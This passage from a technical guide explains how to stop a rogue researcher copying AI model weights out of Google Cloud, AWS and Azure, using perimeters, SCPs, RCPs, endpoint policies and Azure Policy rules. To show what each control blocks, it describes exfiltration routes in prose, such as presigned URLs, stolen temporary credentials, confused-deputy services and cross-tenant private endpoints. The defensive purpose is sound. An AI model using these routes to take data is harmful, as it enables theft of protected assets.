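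Ingress and egress rules usually widen through edits, such as when an engineer in a hurry replaces a list of methods with an asterisk or adds a second partner to the first one's rule. Google allows a request if it matches any one rule, so adding a narrow rule later doesn't tighten a broad one. If a rule names a group of people, adding someone to the group also widens the rule, without any change to the perimeter. For the weights perimeter, the company should avoid groups in egress rules and delete each exception when the work that required it ends. A rule's title can hold up to 100 characters, enough to record who asked for the rule and when it should expire.

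### Limits Google documents

VPC Service Controls doesn't support every Google Cloud service. Google Cloud tells customers not to enable an unsupported service in a perimeter and to put it in a project outside if they need it. For weights, that is only acceptable if the service never needs to touch them. This command lists the supported services:

```
gcloud access-context-manager supported-services list
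```

The output shows whether each service is available through the restricted range, whether it has known limitations, and its stage of support. Services at the "Preview" stage aren't fully supported for production use, so the company should keep weights out of them.

A perimeter may protect only part of a service, even one that is fully supported. For NetApp Volumes, a file storage service, it protects the management interface, but Google Cloud says it doesn't cover reads and writes made with the standard file-sharing protocols, which is how a program would normally load a checkpoint. Similarly, for the database AlloyDB, it protects the administrative interface but not direct connections to the data. Some services also have methods that a perimeter can't control, and others don't let a rule distinguish between methods, so an exception for one method has to allow all of them.

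Perimeters don't fully control access to metadata such as bucket names, which a thief can use to work out which bucket to look for. Google Cloud advises customers to restrict access to metadata through IAM.

For weights, the most serious documented limit is that a perimeter doesn't block third-party services on the internet, such as an AWS bucket the researcher owns. The firewall rules that go with the restricted range would stop an upload to that bucket or to a file-sharing site, but they are configured separately from the perimeter. If someone later opens the firewall so that a test can download public software, the researcher could upload the weights even though the perimeter hasn't changed.

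### Scoped policies and quotas

A scoped policy covers one folder or project and lets the company delegate its perimeters to the administrators of that folder or project. Google Cloud's *Scoped policies* describes them as working alongside the policy for the whole organization. The company needs that wider policy too, because scoped policies may behave unexpectedly without it, which Google Cloud lists as a known issue. A policy's scope can't be changed after the policy is created, according to Google Cloud's *Create a scoped access policy*, so it is best to decide on the folders first. To connect projects under different scoped policies, the company can use ingress and egress rules but not bridges.

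The weights perimeter is better kept in the organization's main policy. Delegating a perimeter is useful when a team knows its own traffic best and the central staff can't keep up with its requests. But delegating the weights perimeter might give control of its exceptions to managers of the researchers it is meant to restrain. The company can still delegate other departments' perimeters.

Google Cloud's *Quotas and limits* sets these limits, which can change:

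| Item | Limit |
|---|---|
| Policies for the whole organization | 1 |
| Scoped policies per organization | 50 |
| Perimeters per policy, including bridges | 10,000 |
| Protected resources per policy | 40,000 |
| VPC networks referenced in a policy's perimeters and ingress rules | 500 |
| Identity groups in a policy's ingress and egress rules | 1,000 |
| Attributes in one perimeter's ingress and egress rules | 6,000 |

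An attribute is a single entry in a rule, such as one project, identity or method. The partner rule above uses five: two methods, one destination project, one identity and one source project. A perimeter could hold 1,200 rules like it before reaching the quota. That is far more exceptions than anyone can review, so a company should set its own, much lower limit for the weights perimeter.

For most of these items, Google counts the enforced configuration together with any dry-run configuration, which logs violations without blocking them. It counts attributes separately for each configuration.

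### Changes in 2025 and 2026

Recent additions make narrow rules easier to write. According to Google Cloud's *VPC Service Controls release notes*, egress rules gained general support in February 2025 for naming a source project. The partner rule depends on this to tie the machine identity to the release project. Since March 2025, customers have also been able to use organization policies to constrain how perimeters are configured, which should let a company forbid new bridges, for example.

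Engineers can also name IAM roles in a rule instead of listing the methods it allows. Google began previewing this feature in March 2025 and made it generally available in April 2026. A role can contain more permissions than the task needs, so listing methods is still the better choice for weights. Rules that name individual AI agents' identities entered preview in March 2026 and became generally available in June. A company that uses agents to run evaluations can give each agent its own narrow exception, or none, without granting the same access to the employee who started it.

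Service patterns, generally available since August 2026, are meant for networks that need an unsupported Google service and therefore can't rely on the restricted range. The company lists the web addresses of the unsupported services it needs, and Google refuses requests to the others. Service patterns can also add a header to allowed requests that limits which organizations' resources they can reach. These controls reduce the risk from unsupported services, but a perimeter still doesn't protect those services, so the weights network should stay on the restricted range if it can.

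The list of supported services also keeps changing. Between January 7 and September 8, 2026, the release notes contain more than two dozen announcements of new or upgraded support, so a protected list that was complete in January would have had gaps by September. In August, Google began previewing a recommender that looks for active, sensitive services outside any perimeter and for mismatches between the protected and accessible lists. It could catch some of these gaps, but because it is a preview feature, it shouldn't replace regularly comparing the company's list with Google's.

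## Writing organization, resource and endpoint policies on AWS

AWS has no single object equivalent to Google's service perimeter, so the company in the example has to build its boundary from three types of policy, each attached to something different. The examples use these invented account numbers and the organization identifier `o-examplecorp`.

| Account | Number | Location |
|---|---|---|
| Weights bucket | 111111111111 | Weights unit |
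| Training | 222222222222 | Weights unit |
| Evaluation | 333333333333 | Weights unit |
| Serving | 444444444444 | Weights unit |
| Release | 555555555555 | Rest of the company |
| Sandbox | 666666666666 | Rest of the company |
| Testing partner | 888888888888 | Partner's organization |
| Researcher's personal account | 999999999999 | Outside account |

### Three perimeters and six objectives

AWS divides its data perimeter into three parts and sets two objectives for each. The identity perimeter concerns who makes a request, the resource perimeter concerns what the request reaches, and the network perimeter concerns where the request comes from.

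| Perimeter | Objective | Policy type | Main condition keys |
|---|---|---|---|
| Identity | Only trusted identities can use the company's resources | Resource control policy | `aws:PrincipalOrgID` |
| Identity | Only trusted identities can send requests from the company's network | VPC endpoint policy | `aws:PrincipalOrgID` |
| Resource | The company's identities can use only trusted resources | Service control policy | `aws:ResourceOrgID` |
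| Resource | Requests from the company's network can reach only trusted resources | VPC endpoint policy | `aws:ResourceOrgID` |
| Network | The company's identities can work only from expected networks | Service control policy | `aws:SourceIp`, `aws:SourceVpc`, `aws:VpceOrgID` |
| Network | The company's resources are open only to expected networks | Resource control policy | `aws:SourceIp`, `aws:SourceVpc`, `aws:VpceOrgID` |

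A service control policy (SCP) limits what identities in the company's accounts may do, regardless of where they connect from or who owns the resource. A resource control policy (RCP) limits what anyone, including identities outside the company, may do to resources in those accounts. Neither type covers the organization's management account, so that account should hold no weights.

A VPC endpoint is a private route from one of the company's networks to an AWS service such as S3, Amazon's object storage. Its endpoint policy limits which requests can use that route.

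None of these policies grants a permission, and if any of them denies a request, AWS refuses it, whatever the others allow.

The policies test condition keys, which are facts AWS collects about each request. `aws:PrincipalOrgID` gives the caller's organization, and `aws:ResourceOrgID` gives the organization that owns the resource. AWS warns against using wildcards with these keys because a pattern could also match an outsider's identifier.

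The table shows four ways the researcher might try to get the checkpoint out, and the policy that stops each.

| What the researcher does | Caller | Bucket | Network | What stops her |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Copies the checkpoint to her own bucket with her work credentials | Company | Outside | Company | SCP |
| Uploads it to her own bucket with her personal credentials | Outside | Outside | Company | Endpoint policy |
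| Reads the weights bucket with her personal credentials | Outside | Company | Home | RCP |
| Reads the weights bucket with her work credentials | Company | Company | Home | Network conditions in an RCP or SCP |

### Work credentials and an outside bucket

The first attempt is the same as in the Google Cloud example. On a test machine in the evaluation account, the researcher tries to copy the checkpoint to a personal bucket that accepts her work identity. This SCP, adapted from AWS, stops her:

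```json
{
  "Version": "2012-10-17",
  "Statement": [
    {
      "Sid": "OnlyCompanyResources",
      "Effect": "Deny",
      "Action": "*",
      "Resource": "*",
      "Condition": {
        "StringNotEqualsIfExists": {
          "aws:ResourceOrgID": "o-examplecorp"
        }
      }
    }
  ]
}
```

- `Version` identifies the edition of the policy language. It has nothing to do with when the company wrote the policy.
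- `Sid` is an optional label for the statement.
- `Effect` is `Deny`, so AWS refuses any request that matches the rest of the statement.
- `Action` and `Resource` are both asterisks, so the statement covers every action on every resource. It has no line for the caller, because an SCP applies to all the identities in the accounts it is attached to.
- `Condition` narrows the statement. `StringNotEquals` is a negated operator, which means that it is true when two values differ. AWS therefore refuses the request if the resource belongs to any organization other than `o-examplecorp`.

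The researcher's personal account might not belong to an organization at all. The request then has no value for `aws:ResourceOrgID`, and it is natural to expect the rule not to apply. In fact it still does, because a negated operator is true when the key is absent. The suffix `IfExists` makes no difference here, and AWS adds it only to make the intention clear. With other operators it changes the result:

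| Operator | Values match | Values differ | Key is absent |
|---|---|---|---|
| `StringEquals` | True | False | False |
| `StringEqualsIfExists` | True | False | True |
| `StringNotEquals` | False | True | True |
| `StringNotEqualsIfExists` | False | True | True |

An `Allow` statement should therefore use plain `StringEquals`, because `StringEqualsIfExists` would also allow requests that have no value for the key.

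An RCP alone wouldn't stop this copy. Suppose the company has no SCP, only an RCP that reserves its buckets for its own identities. AWS checks both the read and the write. The RCP applies to the read because the company owns the weights bucket, but it doesn't block the researcher because she is using a company identity. The RCP doesn't apply to the write because the company doesn't own the destination bucket. AWS's *Resource control policies (RCPs)* explains that an RCP on one account has no effect when that account's users access a bucket in an outside account.

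The SCP covers reading as well as writing, so it also stops staff from downloading data or software from other organizations' buckets. AWS considers this a benefit because these downloads can bring in malicious code. But a company that trains on public datasets or uses AWS-owned buckets will need exceptions.

The SCP doesn't stop the researcher from copying the checkpoint to the sandbox, which belongs to the same organization. To prevent that, the company can attach a second SCP to the weights unit that uses `aws:ResourceAccount` to block requests to resources outside the unit's four accounts, with exceptions for the logs and scores that have to leave. This policy applies only to identities in those four accounts. If the researcher also has an identity in the sandbox account, the company needs other rules to restrict that identity.

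### Personal credentials on the company's network

Next, the researcher uses her work identity to save the checkpoint to the test machine's disk, which the company permits. Then, on the same machine, she enters the access keys for her personal account and uploads the file to her own bucket.

The SCP doesn't apply to this upload, because her personal identity doesn't belong to the company's organization. No company RCP applies either, because the bucket is hers. The company controls only the network, so it needs a policy on the endpoint that connects the network to S3. This is the statement AWS recommends:

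```json
{
  "Effect": "Allow",
  "Principal": "*",
  "Action": "*",
  "Resource": "*",
  "Condition": {
    "StringEquals": {
      "aws:PrincipalOrgID": "o-examplecorp",
      "aws:ResourceOrgID": "o-examplecorp"
    }
  }
}
```

Here, `Allow` sets the most that any caller can do through the endpoint, but doesn't grant any permissions. Both the caller and the bucket must belong to the company, and the researcher's upload fails because neither does. It fails even if her personal account belongs to no organization, because both keys are then absent and `StringEquals` is false.

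She could try to keep her keys off the machine by using a presigned URL, a web address that lets anyone who has it perform one action with the permissions of whoever created it. At home, she uses her personal account to create a URL for uploading to her bucket, then opens it on the test machine. According to AWS, the caller in such a request is the identity that generated the URL, so the endpoint policy refuses this upload too.

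The policy contains the organization's full identifier. To make one policy work in several organizations, an engineer might instead deny any request in which `aws:ResourceOrgID` differs from `${aws:PrincipalOrgID}`, a variable that AWS replaces with the identifier of the caller's own organization. AWS warns against doing this in an endpoint policy. If the researcher has set up an organization for her personal account, her identity and bucket in that account both belong to it, so the values match and the upload goes through. The comparison is safe in an SCP, which applies only to the company's own identities.

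AWS suggests a replacement that uses a single `StringNotEquals` to compare each key with the company's identifier. When several keys appear under one operator, the statement takes effect only if every comparison is true, so this denial applies only if neither the caller nor the bucket belongs to the company. The table compares this version with the other two, assuming that a broad `Allow` accompanies each denial.

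| Caller's organization | Bucket's organization | Deny if the two differ | Deny if neither is the company's | Allow only if both are the company's |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Company | Company | Passes | Passes | Passes |
| Company | Researcher's | Refused | Passes | Refused |
| Researcher's | Researcher's | Passes | Refused | Refused |
| Researcher's | Company | Refused | Passes | Refused |

AWS's replacement stops the upload made with personal credentials but relies on the company's SCP and RCP for the two mixed cases. The last version stops all three, so it is the better choice for a network that carries model weights.

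In the weights unit's networks, the policy should also test `aws:PrincipalAccount` and `aws:ResourceAccount` against the unit's account numbers. Otherwise the researcher could enter her sandbox credentials on the test machine and upload the checkpoint to the sandbox. The company again has to make exceptions for logs and scores.

Some ordinary traffic needs exceptions too. Amazon Linux downloads updates from AWS's own buckets without identifying the caller, so AWS adds a statement allowing anyone to read from those buckets. The statement permits only `s3:GetObject`, which downloads a file, so nobody can use it to upload data.

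An endpoint policy only controls requests that go through its endpoint. If the test machine can reach S3's public addresses over the internet, the researcher can upload the checkpoint that way. Requests to another AWS region may also bypass the endpoint. Some services don't support endpoint policies, and according to Spectral's *Ensure that VPC Endpoint policy does not provide excessive permissions*, their endpoints allow full access. The company should create endpoints only for the services its machines need and close the other routes with network controls.

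### An outside identity and the weights bucket

The researcher could also make the copy from outside. If she is allowed to edit the weights bucket's policy, she can give her personal account read access, then download the checkpoint at home using her personal identity. The SCP doesn't apply to that identity, and the request never passes through a company endpoint.

AWS (2024) introduced RCPs with almost this case in mind, giving as its example a rule that no outside identity can use the organization's buckets, whatever the individual bucket policies permit. The RCP denies all S3 actions under these conditions, which AWS recommends:

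```json
"Condition": {
  "StringNotEqualsIfExists": {
    "aws:PrincipalOrgID": "o-examplecorp"
  },
  "BoolIfExists": {
    "aws:PrincipalIsAWSService": "false"
  }
}
```

AWS refuses the request only if both conditions are true. The researcher's personal identity belongs to another organization or to none, and it isn't an AWS service, so her download fails. The second condition is needed because AWS services sometimes use their own identities, which belong to no customer's organization. Without it, the RCP would stop AWS from writing audit logs to the company's buckets.

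The second condition needs `IfExists` to block anonymous requests, which have no value for `aws:PrincipalIsAWSService`. With plain `Bool`, the condition would be false for such a request and the statement wouldn't apply, so if someone made the bucket public by mistake, a stranger could download the checkpoint without logging in. `BoolIfExists` is true when the key is absent, so AWS refuses the request.

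Someone with an outside account can also exploit the exemption for AWS services by setting up a service there and pointing it at the company's bucket. The service then makes the request under AWS's identity. This is a confused deputy problem, in which a program uses its authority on behalf of somebody who shouldn't have it. AWS's RCP includes a second statement that checks `aws:SourceOrgID`, the organization the service is acting for, and denies the request if that organization isn't the company's.

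The researcher might also target a role, which is an identity that other identities can temporarily take on. If she can edit the list of who may use a role in the evaluation account, she can add her personal identity. She can then take on the role at home and read the bucket as a company identity, which the S3 rule permits. To stop this, the company needs a similar RCP for the Security Token Service (STS), which issues credentials for roles. *AWS RCP Support by Service*, a guide from the cloud security vendor Native, lists this use of the organization key.

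A third RCP can protect encryption keys in AWS's Key Management Service (KMS). If the company encrypts the checkpoint with a key it manages, an outside identity needs permission to use that key as well as to read the file. The RCP can't protect keys that AWS manages for the company.

For the narrower boundary, the company should attach another RCP to the weights unit and have it test `aws:PrincipalAccount` against the four account numbers. Her sandbox identity then can't read the weights bucket, even if someone adds it to the bucket policy.

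### Work credentials on an unexpected network

In the last attempt, the caller and the bucket both belong to the company. The researcher copies the test machine's temporary credentials to her laptop, goes home and uses them to download the checkpoint before they expire. An outsider who steals the credentials can do the same. After the download, no AWS policy can control where the file goes.

The company can stop this with an RCP that tests where the request comes from. The standard version, from AWS, permits requests from the company's office addresses and from any endpoint the organization owns. That is too broad for weights. The researcher could take her laptop to the office, download the checkpoint there and upload it from home. The weights bucket should accept downloads only through endpoints in the three accounts that run the model:

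```json
"Condition": {
  "StringNotEqualsIfExists": {
    "aws:VpceAccount": ["222222222222", "333333333333", "444444444444"]
  },
  "BoolIfExists": {
    "aws:PrincipalIsAWSService": "false",
    "aws:ViaAWSService": "false"
  }
}
```

The statement should deny only actions that begin with `s3:GetObject`, so that administrators can still manage the bucket from the office. A read request from the laptop doesn't pass through an endpoint, so it has no value for `aws:VpceAccount` and AWS refuses it.

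The last two lines exempt AWS services. `aws:ViaAWSService` is true when a service uses the researcher's credentials to make another request for her, as S3 does when it calls KMS to encrypt a file. These requests come from AWS's network, so they would fail without the exemption. The exemption also means the network rule won't stop a service from reading the weights on her behalf.

Other services take on a role the company has created for them. S3 replication, which automatically copies new files to another bucket, works this way, and the network rule blocks it. AWS suggests tagging the role and exempting anything with that tag. This is safe only if the company also restricts who can change tags and keeps the RCP against outside identities. Otherwise an outsider could put the same tag on a role in his own account. For the weights bucket, the company should leave out the tag exemption unless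 it needs automatic replication.

The company can set a similar rule on its identities with an SCP, which would also stop the researcher from using her work credentials at home to reach resources that RCPs don't cover. This rule is harder to apply widely. If it covered every identity, it would break AWS Glue, a data-processing service that can read files from inside the company's network but uses the same role to set up its network connections from AWS's side. AWS therefore advises companies to tag the identities with the highest risk of misuse and apply the rule only to those. In the example, these are the roles that can read the weights, including the test machines' roles. One of AWS's published samples for this SCP nests two operators inside a third, so it is safer to copy the layout of its RCP sample.

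When AWS issues credentials to a rented machine, the company can block their use outside that machine's network without keeping a list of networks. `aws:Ec2InstanceSourceVpc` records the network where AWS delivered the credentials, and `aws:SourceVpc` records the network whose endpoint the request came through. An SCP can deny any request in which the two differ. AWS notes that `aws:SourceVpc` is empty for requests to a public address, so credentials copied to a laptop stop working. With a second pair of keys, the SCP can also compare the machine's private address with the address that sent the request, which stops the researcher from using the credentials on another machine in the same network.

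Before August 2025, a company had to list each network or endpoint in its policies and update the list whenever it added one. AWS (2025) then introduced the condition keys `aws:VpceAccount`, `aws:VpceOrgPaths` and `aws:VpceOrgID`, which identify the account, organizational unit or organization that owns the endpoint. The existing rule automatically covers any new endpoint in the evaluation account.

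Some services don't supply these keys, and with the condition above they would refuse even requests from the company's own endpoints. For those services, AWS recommends `aws:SourceVpc` with a region check, because networks in different regions can have the same identifier. AWS (2025) added `aws:SourceVpcArn` in November, which gives the network's full name and lets a policy restrict access to endpoints in chosen regions.

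Since June, AWS has let companies use an RCP to restrict web console sign-in to expected networks (AWS, 2026). AWS checks the rule at sign-in and whenever the session requests new credentials, so a researcher who signs in at the office and then takes her laptop home should lose access at the next request.

### An exception for the testing partner

The release account sends scores to the partner's bucket, `partner-scores`, in account 888888888888. The SCP that restricts staff to company resources would block this. The version below lets the scores through:

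```json
{
  "Version": "2012-10-17",
  "Statement": [
    {
      "Sid": "OnlyCompanyResources",
      "Effect": "Deny",
      "Action": "*",
      "NotResource": "arn:aws:s3:::partner-scores/*",
      "Condition": {
        "StringNotEqualsIfExists": {
          "aws:ResourceOrgID": "o-examplecorp"
        }
      }
    },
    {
      "Sid": "PartnerMustOwnBucket",
      "Effect": "Deny",
      "Action": "*",
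      "Resource": "arn:aws:s3:::partner-scores/*",
      "Condition": {
        "StringNotEqualsIfExists": {
          "aws:ResourceAccount": "888888888888"
        }
      }
    },
    {
      "Sid": "OnlyReleaseRole",
      "Effect": "Deny",
      "Action": "*",
      "Resource": "arn:aws:s3:::partner-scores/*",
      "Condition": {
        "ArnNotLikeIfExists": {
          "aws:PrincipalArn": "arn:aws:iam::555555555555:role/score-release"
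        }
      }
    }
  ]
}
```

The first statement replaces `Resource` with `NotResource`, so it covers everything except files in the partner's bucket. The string that begins with `arn` is an Amazon Resource Name, AWS's full name for a resource, and it contains the bucket's name but not its owner.

The second statement makes AWS refuse the copy unless the bucket owner's account number matches the partner's. If the partner deletes the bucket, someone else can create a new one with the same name. Without the second statement, the researcher could do that in her personal account, and the exception would let her copy the checkpoint there.

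Those two statements follow AWS's pattern, which lets every identity the SCP covers use the exception. The third statement limits the exception to the role that sends the scores, for the same reason that the Google Cloud rule names a single machine identity.

The company can attach this SCP to the whole organization. The weights unit's own stricter SCP, which has no exception for the partner, still applies because a request has to satisfy the policies at every level. If the release program reaches S3 through an endpoint, the endpoint's policy also needs a statement that allows company identities to use the partner's bucket and, like the SCP, specifies the account number.

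The SCP opens a single bucket, which makes it narrower than Google's egress rule for the partner's whole project.

The partner could instead fetch the scores from a company bucket. The company would then have to add the partner's account number to the RCP that blocks outside identities and, if the bucket has a network rule, add the partner's endpoints to that rule. In AWS's sample, the account exception applies to every bucket the RCP covers, so the other buckets' own policies would have to keep the partner out. Sending the scores from the release account avoids these exceptions.

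Exceptions like these were harder to write until 2025, because an SCP couldn't use `NotResource` in a denial. Companies instead tagged each identity that needed to reach outside resources. Tagging the wrong identity, by accident or on purpose, exempted it from the rule. According to AWS's *Unlock new possibilities*, SCPs now support the full policy language, including conditions on `Allow` statements and wildcards anywhere in an action's name. AWS still recommends one broad `Allow` followed by specific denials, because a second, looser `Allow` can undo a strict one without anyone noticing.

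### Which services RCPs cover

RCPs apply only to services that AWS supports for them. At launch in November 2024, these were S3, STS, KMS, Simple Queue Service (which passes messages between programs) and Secrets Manager (which stores passwords and keys). In June 2025, AWS added OpenSearch Serverless, a search service, and Elastic Container Registry, which stores container images (AWS, 2025). Until then, no RCP could stop an outside identity from downloading an image that contained model weights if the registry's own policy allowed the download.

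On January 22, AWS (2026) extended resource control policies (RCPs) to CloudWatch Logs and to Cognito, which manages user accounts for applications. AWS (2026) added the database DynamoDB on February 12. The list of supported services has grown much faster since then. The main edition of AWS's documentation had 25 entries in early July, and Native counted 44 on August 11. In October, the edition of AWS's *Resource control policies (RCPs)* for the European Sovereign Cloud, a separate part of AWS for European customers, had 62. That edition's list may not match the one for standard AWS, and some of the increase could come from AWS splitting one service into several entries, as it has done with Cognito. A company should check the current list for the part of AWS it uses.

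None of the three lists includes SageMaker, AWS's machine learning platform, or the part of EC2 that manages disk snapshots and machine images. For a resource outside the list, AWS suggests attaching a similar rule directly to the resource, if the service supports resource-based policies. That rule is weaker than an RCP because anyone who can edit the resource's policy can remove it.

Native points out that an RCP written for S3 won't start covering DynamoDB when AWS adds RCP support for it, because each service needs its own statement. AWS's Control Tower, a tool for managing many accounts, offers ready-made RCPs, but as of August 2026 only for the original five services. A company therefore has to write its own statement for Elastic Container Registry, and for any other listed service that ends up holding a copy of the weights.

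## Closing cross-tenant copying on Azure

Azure has no equivalent of `aws:ResourceOrgID`, the condition key that lets an AWS policy refuse requests to resources the company doesn't own. So the company has to close each route to another tenant separately, using settings on its networks, storage and sign-ins. In the example, the company keeps the weights in a dedicated tenant.

| Environment | Subscriptions | Tenant |
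|---|---|---|
| Weights storage, training, evaluation, serving | One each | Weights tenant |
| Scores waiting for release | One | Weights tenant |
| Release, sandbox | One each | Main company tenant |
| Testing partner | The partner's | Partner's tenant |
| Researcher's personal storage | Her own | Personal tenant |

Azure keeps files in storage accounts, and each account has a public web address. The weights are at `companyweights.blob.core.windows.net`, and the researcher's own account is at `herbackup.blob.core.windows.net`.

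### What a private endpoint does

A private endpoint uses Microsoft's Private Link technology to give one Azure resource an address inside a company's private network. To set one up for the weights, an engineer chooses a subnet of the evaluation network and enters the storage account's resource ID. Azure then assigns the endpoint an address in that subnet, such as 10.0.1.5. Someone with rights over the storage account has to approve the connection, unless Azure approves it automatically. The engineer also configures the network's DNS to resolve `companyweights.blob.core.windows.net` to 10.0.1.5. When a test machine opens the checkpoint, the traffic stays on Microsoft's network and can reach only that account.

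Microsoft's *Secure your Azure Private Link deployment* presents this one-to-one mapping as a protection against data theft, since nobody can use the endpoint to reach another account. But the endpoint doesn't restrict other routes, so if the test machine can also reach public addresses, the researcher can read the checkpoint through 10.0.1.5 and upload it to `herbackup`.

Microsoft recommends disabling public network access to a resource once its private endpoint works. Doing this on the weights account stops her from downloading the checkpoint to her laptop at home, but not from uploading it to `herbackup`, because she decides whether that account accepts public traffic. The company therefore needs a firewall that blocks outgoing connections from the weights networks except to a short list of destinations. That list must not include `*.blob.core.windows.net` or Azure's ready-made list of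 storage addresses, because both cover every customer's accounts.

An older feature, the service endpoint, makes this harder by giving part of a network a direct route to a whole Azure service. Journey of the Geek's *Network Security Perimeters*, a series of posts by an Azure practitioner, calls service endpoints a wide-open route for data theft, because the traffic bypasses the customer's firewall and can reach any customer's storage account. Microsoft offers service endpoint policies that name the storage accounts a network may reach and block the rest. Private endpoints are still the better choice for weights, because they also work with the perimeters described below.

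### Private endpoints that lead to another tenant

A private endpoint can also connect two tenants. Microsoft's *Limit cross-tenant private endpoint connections in Azure* describes two ways a rogue administrator could use this and gives a rule against each. The rules use Azure Policy, a service that checks requests to create or change resources, but not requests to read or write files. A rule that denies new endpoints won't remove existing ones, so an engineer should look for existing ones first.

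In one case, the administrator creates a private endpoint inside the company's network that leads to an outside resource. This requires permission to create private endpoints and attach them to that network. In the example, the researcher persuades an administrator with these permissions to create an endpoint for `herbackup` in the evaluation network. She then approves the connection from her own tenant and can upload the checkpoint to a private address. The firewall may never check that traffic.

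The endpoint may also let her copy directly between the two accounts, by having her client ask the destination account to fetch a file from the source. According to Microsoft's *Generally available* (2021), Azure Storage first checks that the client has access to both accounts. Microsoft says these copies can fail when the accounts' private endpoints are in different networks, and suggests adding an endpoint for the destination to the source's network. Here, that would be an endpoint for `herbackup` in the evaluation network.

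Adapted for the weights tenant, Microsoft's rule against such endpoints works like this:

1. Azure Policy picks out requests that create or change a private endpoint.
2. It reads the resource ID of the endpoint's target. An endpoint can name its target in either of two fields, `privateLinkServiceConnections` and `manualPrivateLinkServiceConnections`, so the rule checks both.
3. It splits the ID at the slashes to find the subscription that holds the target. A resource ID begins `/subscriptions/`, followed by the subscription's own ID.
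4. It looks for that subscription in `allowedSubscriptions`, a list that the company maintains. If the subscription isn't there, Azure refuses to create the endpoint.

The rule compares subscriptions because a resource ID doesn't contain the tenant. Microsoft's original version requires the endpoint and its target to be in the same subscription. That would also block the endpoint the evaluation network needs, because the weights account is in a different subscription of the same tenant. Microsoft suggests granting exemptions for these cases and advises against a list of allowed subscriptions, since someone has to update it for every new subscription. With only five subscriptions in the weights tenant, a list is practical. It is also safer, because an exemption turns the rule off for everything in its scope, including an endpoint to `herbackup`.

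In the other case, the administrator connects an outside network to a company resource through a private endpoint. The administrator needs write access to the resource to approve the connection. The researcher could then start a machine in her personal tenant, sign in with her work account and download the checkpoint. Disabling public access doesn't prevent this, because the request arrives through the private endpoint.

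Microsoft's rule against this checks each request that would mark a private endpoint connection on a storage account as `Approved`. With the same adaptation, it reads the subscription from the endpoint's ID, and Azure refuses the approval if that subscription isn't on the allowed list. Azure also refuses if the request doesn't identify the endpoint. Engineers can still reject or remove a connection. Azure's web portal leaves out the endpoint's ID, so engineers have to use the command line for legitimate approvals. The rule covers only storage, and Microsoft says to write similar ones for other services, such as Key Vault, which stores encryption keys.

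Microsoft recommends setting this rule to `Audit`, which records violations without blocking them, because `Deny` interferes with Data Factory, a service that moves data between storage systems. `Deny` is better for the weights tenant, because a single outside endpoint is enough to leak the weights.

Data Factory also needs its own rule, because it can create private endpoints in a network that Microsoft manages, where the rule for ordinary endpoints doesn't apply. Microsoft's rule denies these endpoints if they connect to resources outside the factory's subscription, or outside a list of allowed subscriptions. Nobody in the example needs Data Factory to run tests, so the company can forbid it in the weights tenant.

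Microsoft recommends assigning these rules to the top-level management group, which contains all of a tenant's subscriptions. Anyone who can change the assignment can remove the protection.

### Network security perimeters

A network security perimeter is a group of Azure resources with shared rules for traffic through their public addresses. It resembles Google's service perimeter but covers fewer services. Journey of the Geek describes these Azure perimeters as best suited to services where customers upload data but don't control the code. The researcher's test machine, where she can run any program, can't be a member.

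Perimeters became generally available in August 2025, according to Journey of the Geek. Support for storage accounts followed in September, as Vishnu Charan TJ (2025), in *Protect your Storage accounts using network security perimeter*, announced for Microsoft. This was the coverage that Microsoft listed in May 2026:

| Status | Services |
|---|---|
| Generally available | Storage, Key Vault, Azure Monitor, AI Search, Event Hubs, Service Bus, Microsoft Foundry |
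| Preview | Cosmos DB, SQL Database, Azure OpenAI |

In July, Microsoft's documentation for the Chinese edition of Azure still listed Cosmos DB and SQL Database as previews. Neither list includes Azure's container registry, its managed disks or Azure Machine Learning, all of which can hold weights. A company that keeps weights in those services has to protect them with each service's own settings.

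Every perimeter contains one or more profiles, which are sets of rules for particular resources. An inbound rule admits requests from an IP address range or an Azure subscription. An outbound rule lets a resource contact an outside domain name. Direction refers to the request, as on Google Cloud, so a stranger downloading the checkpoint counts as inbound.

The weights account should have no inbound rules. As on AWS, a rule for the office's addresses would let the researcher carry the checkpoint out on her laptop. Microsoft says a subscription rule admits every resource in that subscription. Outbound rules identify an account by name, not owner, so they carry the same risk of a reused name as the AWS exception for the partner's bucket.

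A resource joins a perimeter in one of two modes. In transition mode (formerly learning mode), Azure tries the perimeter's rules first and falls back on the resource's own settings if no rule matches. This lets engineers see in the logs which traffic they would break. In enforced mode, only the perimeter's rules count. A separate setting controls public access to the resource, and Microsoft's *Transition to a network security perimeter in Azure* describes how the two interact:

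| Public access setting | No perimeter | Transition mode | Enforced mode |
|---|---|---|---|
| Enabled | Inbound follows the resource's rules; outbound open | Inbound follows both sets of rules; outbound open | Perimeter rules only |
| Disabled | Inbound blocked; outbound open | Inbound follows perimeter rules; outbound open | Perimeter rules only |
| Secured by perimeter | Both blocked | Perimeter rules only | Perimeter rules only |

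Disabling public access leaves outbound traffic open until the resource is in an enforced perimeter. "Secured by perimeter" is the best setting for the weights account because it blocks both inbound and outbound traffic, even if an engineer forgets to add the resource to a perimeter or later removes it.

Perimeter rules don't apply to traffic through private endpoints, which Microsoft regards as highly secure. This exemption makes sense against strangers on the internet, because someone with rights over the account has approved each endpoint, but it makes less sense against insiders. Vishnu Charan TJ says that perimeter rules stop an attacker with stolen credentials from connecting through an unapproved network. But they won't stop the researcher from reading the checkpoint on her test machine, or an outsider from using an endpoint that a rogue administrator approved, so the company still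 needs the Azure Policy rules above.

Resources inside a perimeter can communicate with each other whenever permissions allow, so the weights perimeter should have few members. It needs the weights account and, if the company manages its own encryption key, the key vault that holds the key. It also needs a destination for diagnostic logs, because an enforced perimeter blocks storage accounts from sending them outside.

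Many companies collect logs in one central workspace, but a resource can belong to only one perimeter, so the workspace can't join every perimeter that sends it logs. Microsoft has begun offering links between perimeters, which automatically create matching inbound and outbound rules. In July 2026, Journey of the Geek reported that links were in public preview, worked for only some of the supported services and were limited to 10 per perimeter, too few for central logging in a large company. A link can apply to all profiles or only to chosen ones. The company should avoid using links for the weights while they are in preview. If it uses one later, it should connect only the profiles that handle logs, so that the link doesn't open a route between storage accounts.

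A workspace inside a perimeter also can't run the detection rules of Microsoft Sentinel, a security monitoring product. Linking two perimeters wouldn't solve this, because the workspace in the second perimeter would have the same limit. The company could instead send the logs to an event hub (a service that passes messages between programs) in the weights perimeter, and have a program forward them to a workspace outside any perimeter.

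Enforced mode restricts a storage account in other ways. Azure Backup doesn't support accounts in a perimeter, so the company needs another way to keep a spare copy. Programs can reach the account only over HTTPS, which rules out some training systems that mount it as a shared disk. The perimeter also prevents object replication, Azure's counterpart to S3 replication, which is welcome for weights because replication could copy them to an outside account.

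### Blocking sign-ins to other tenants

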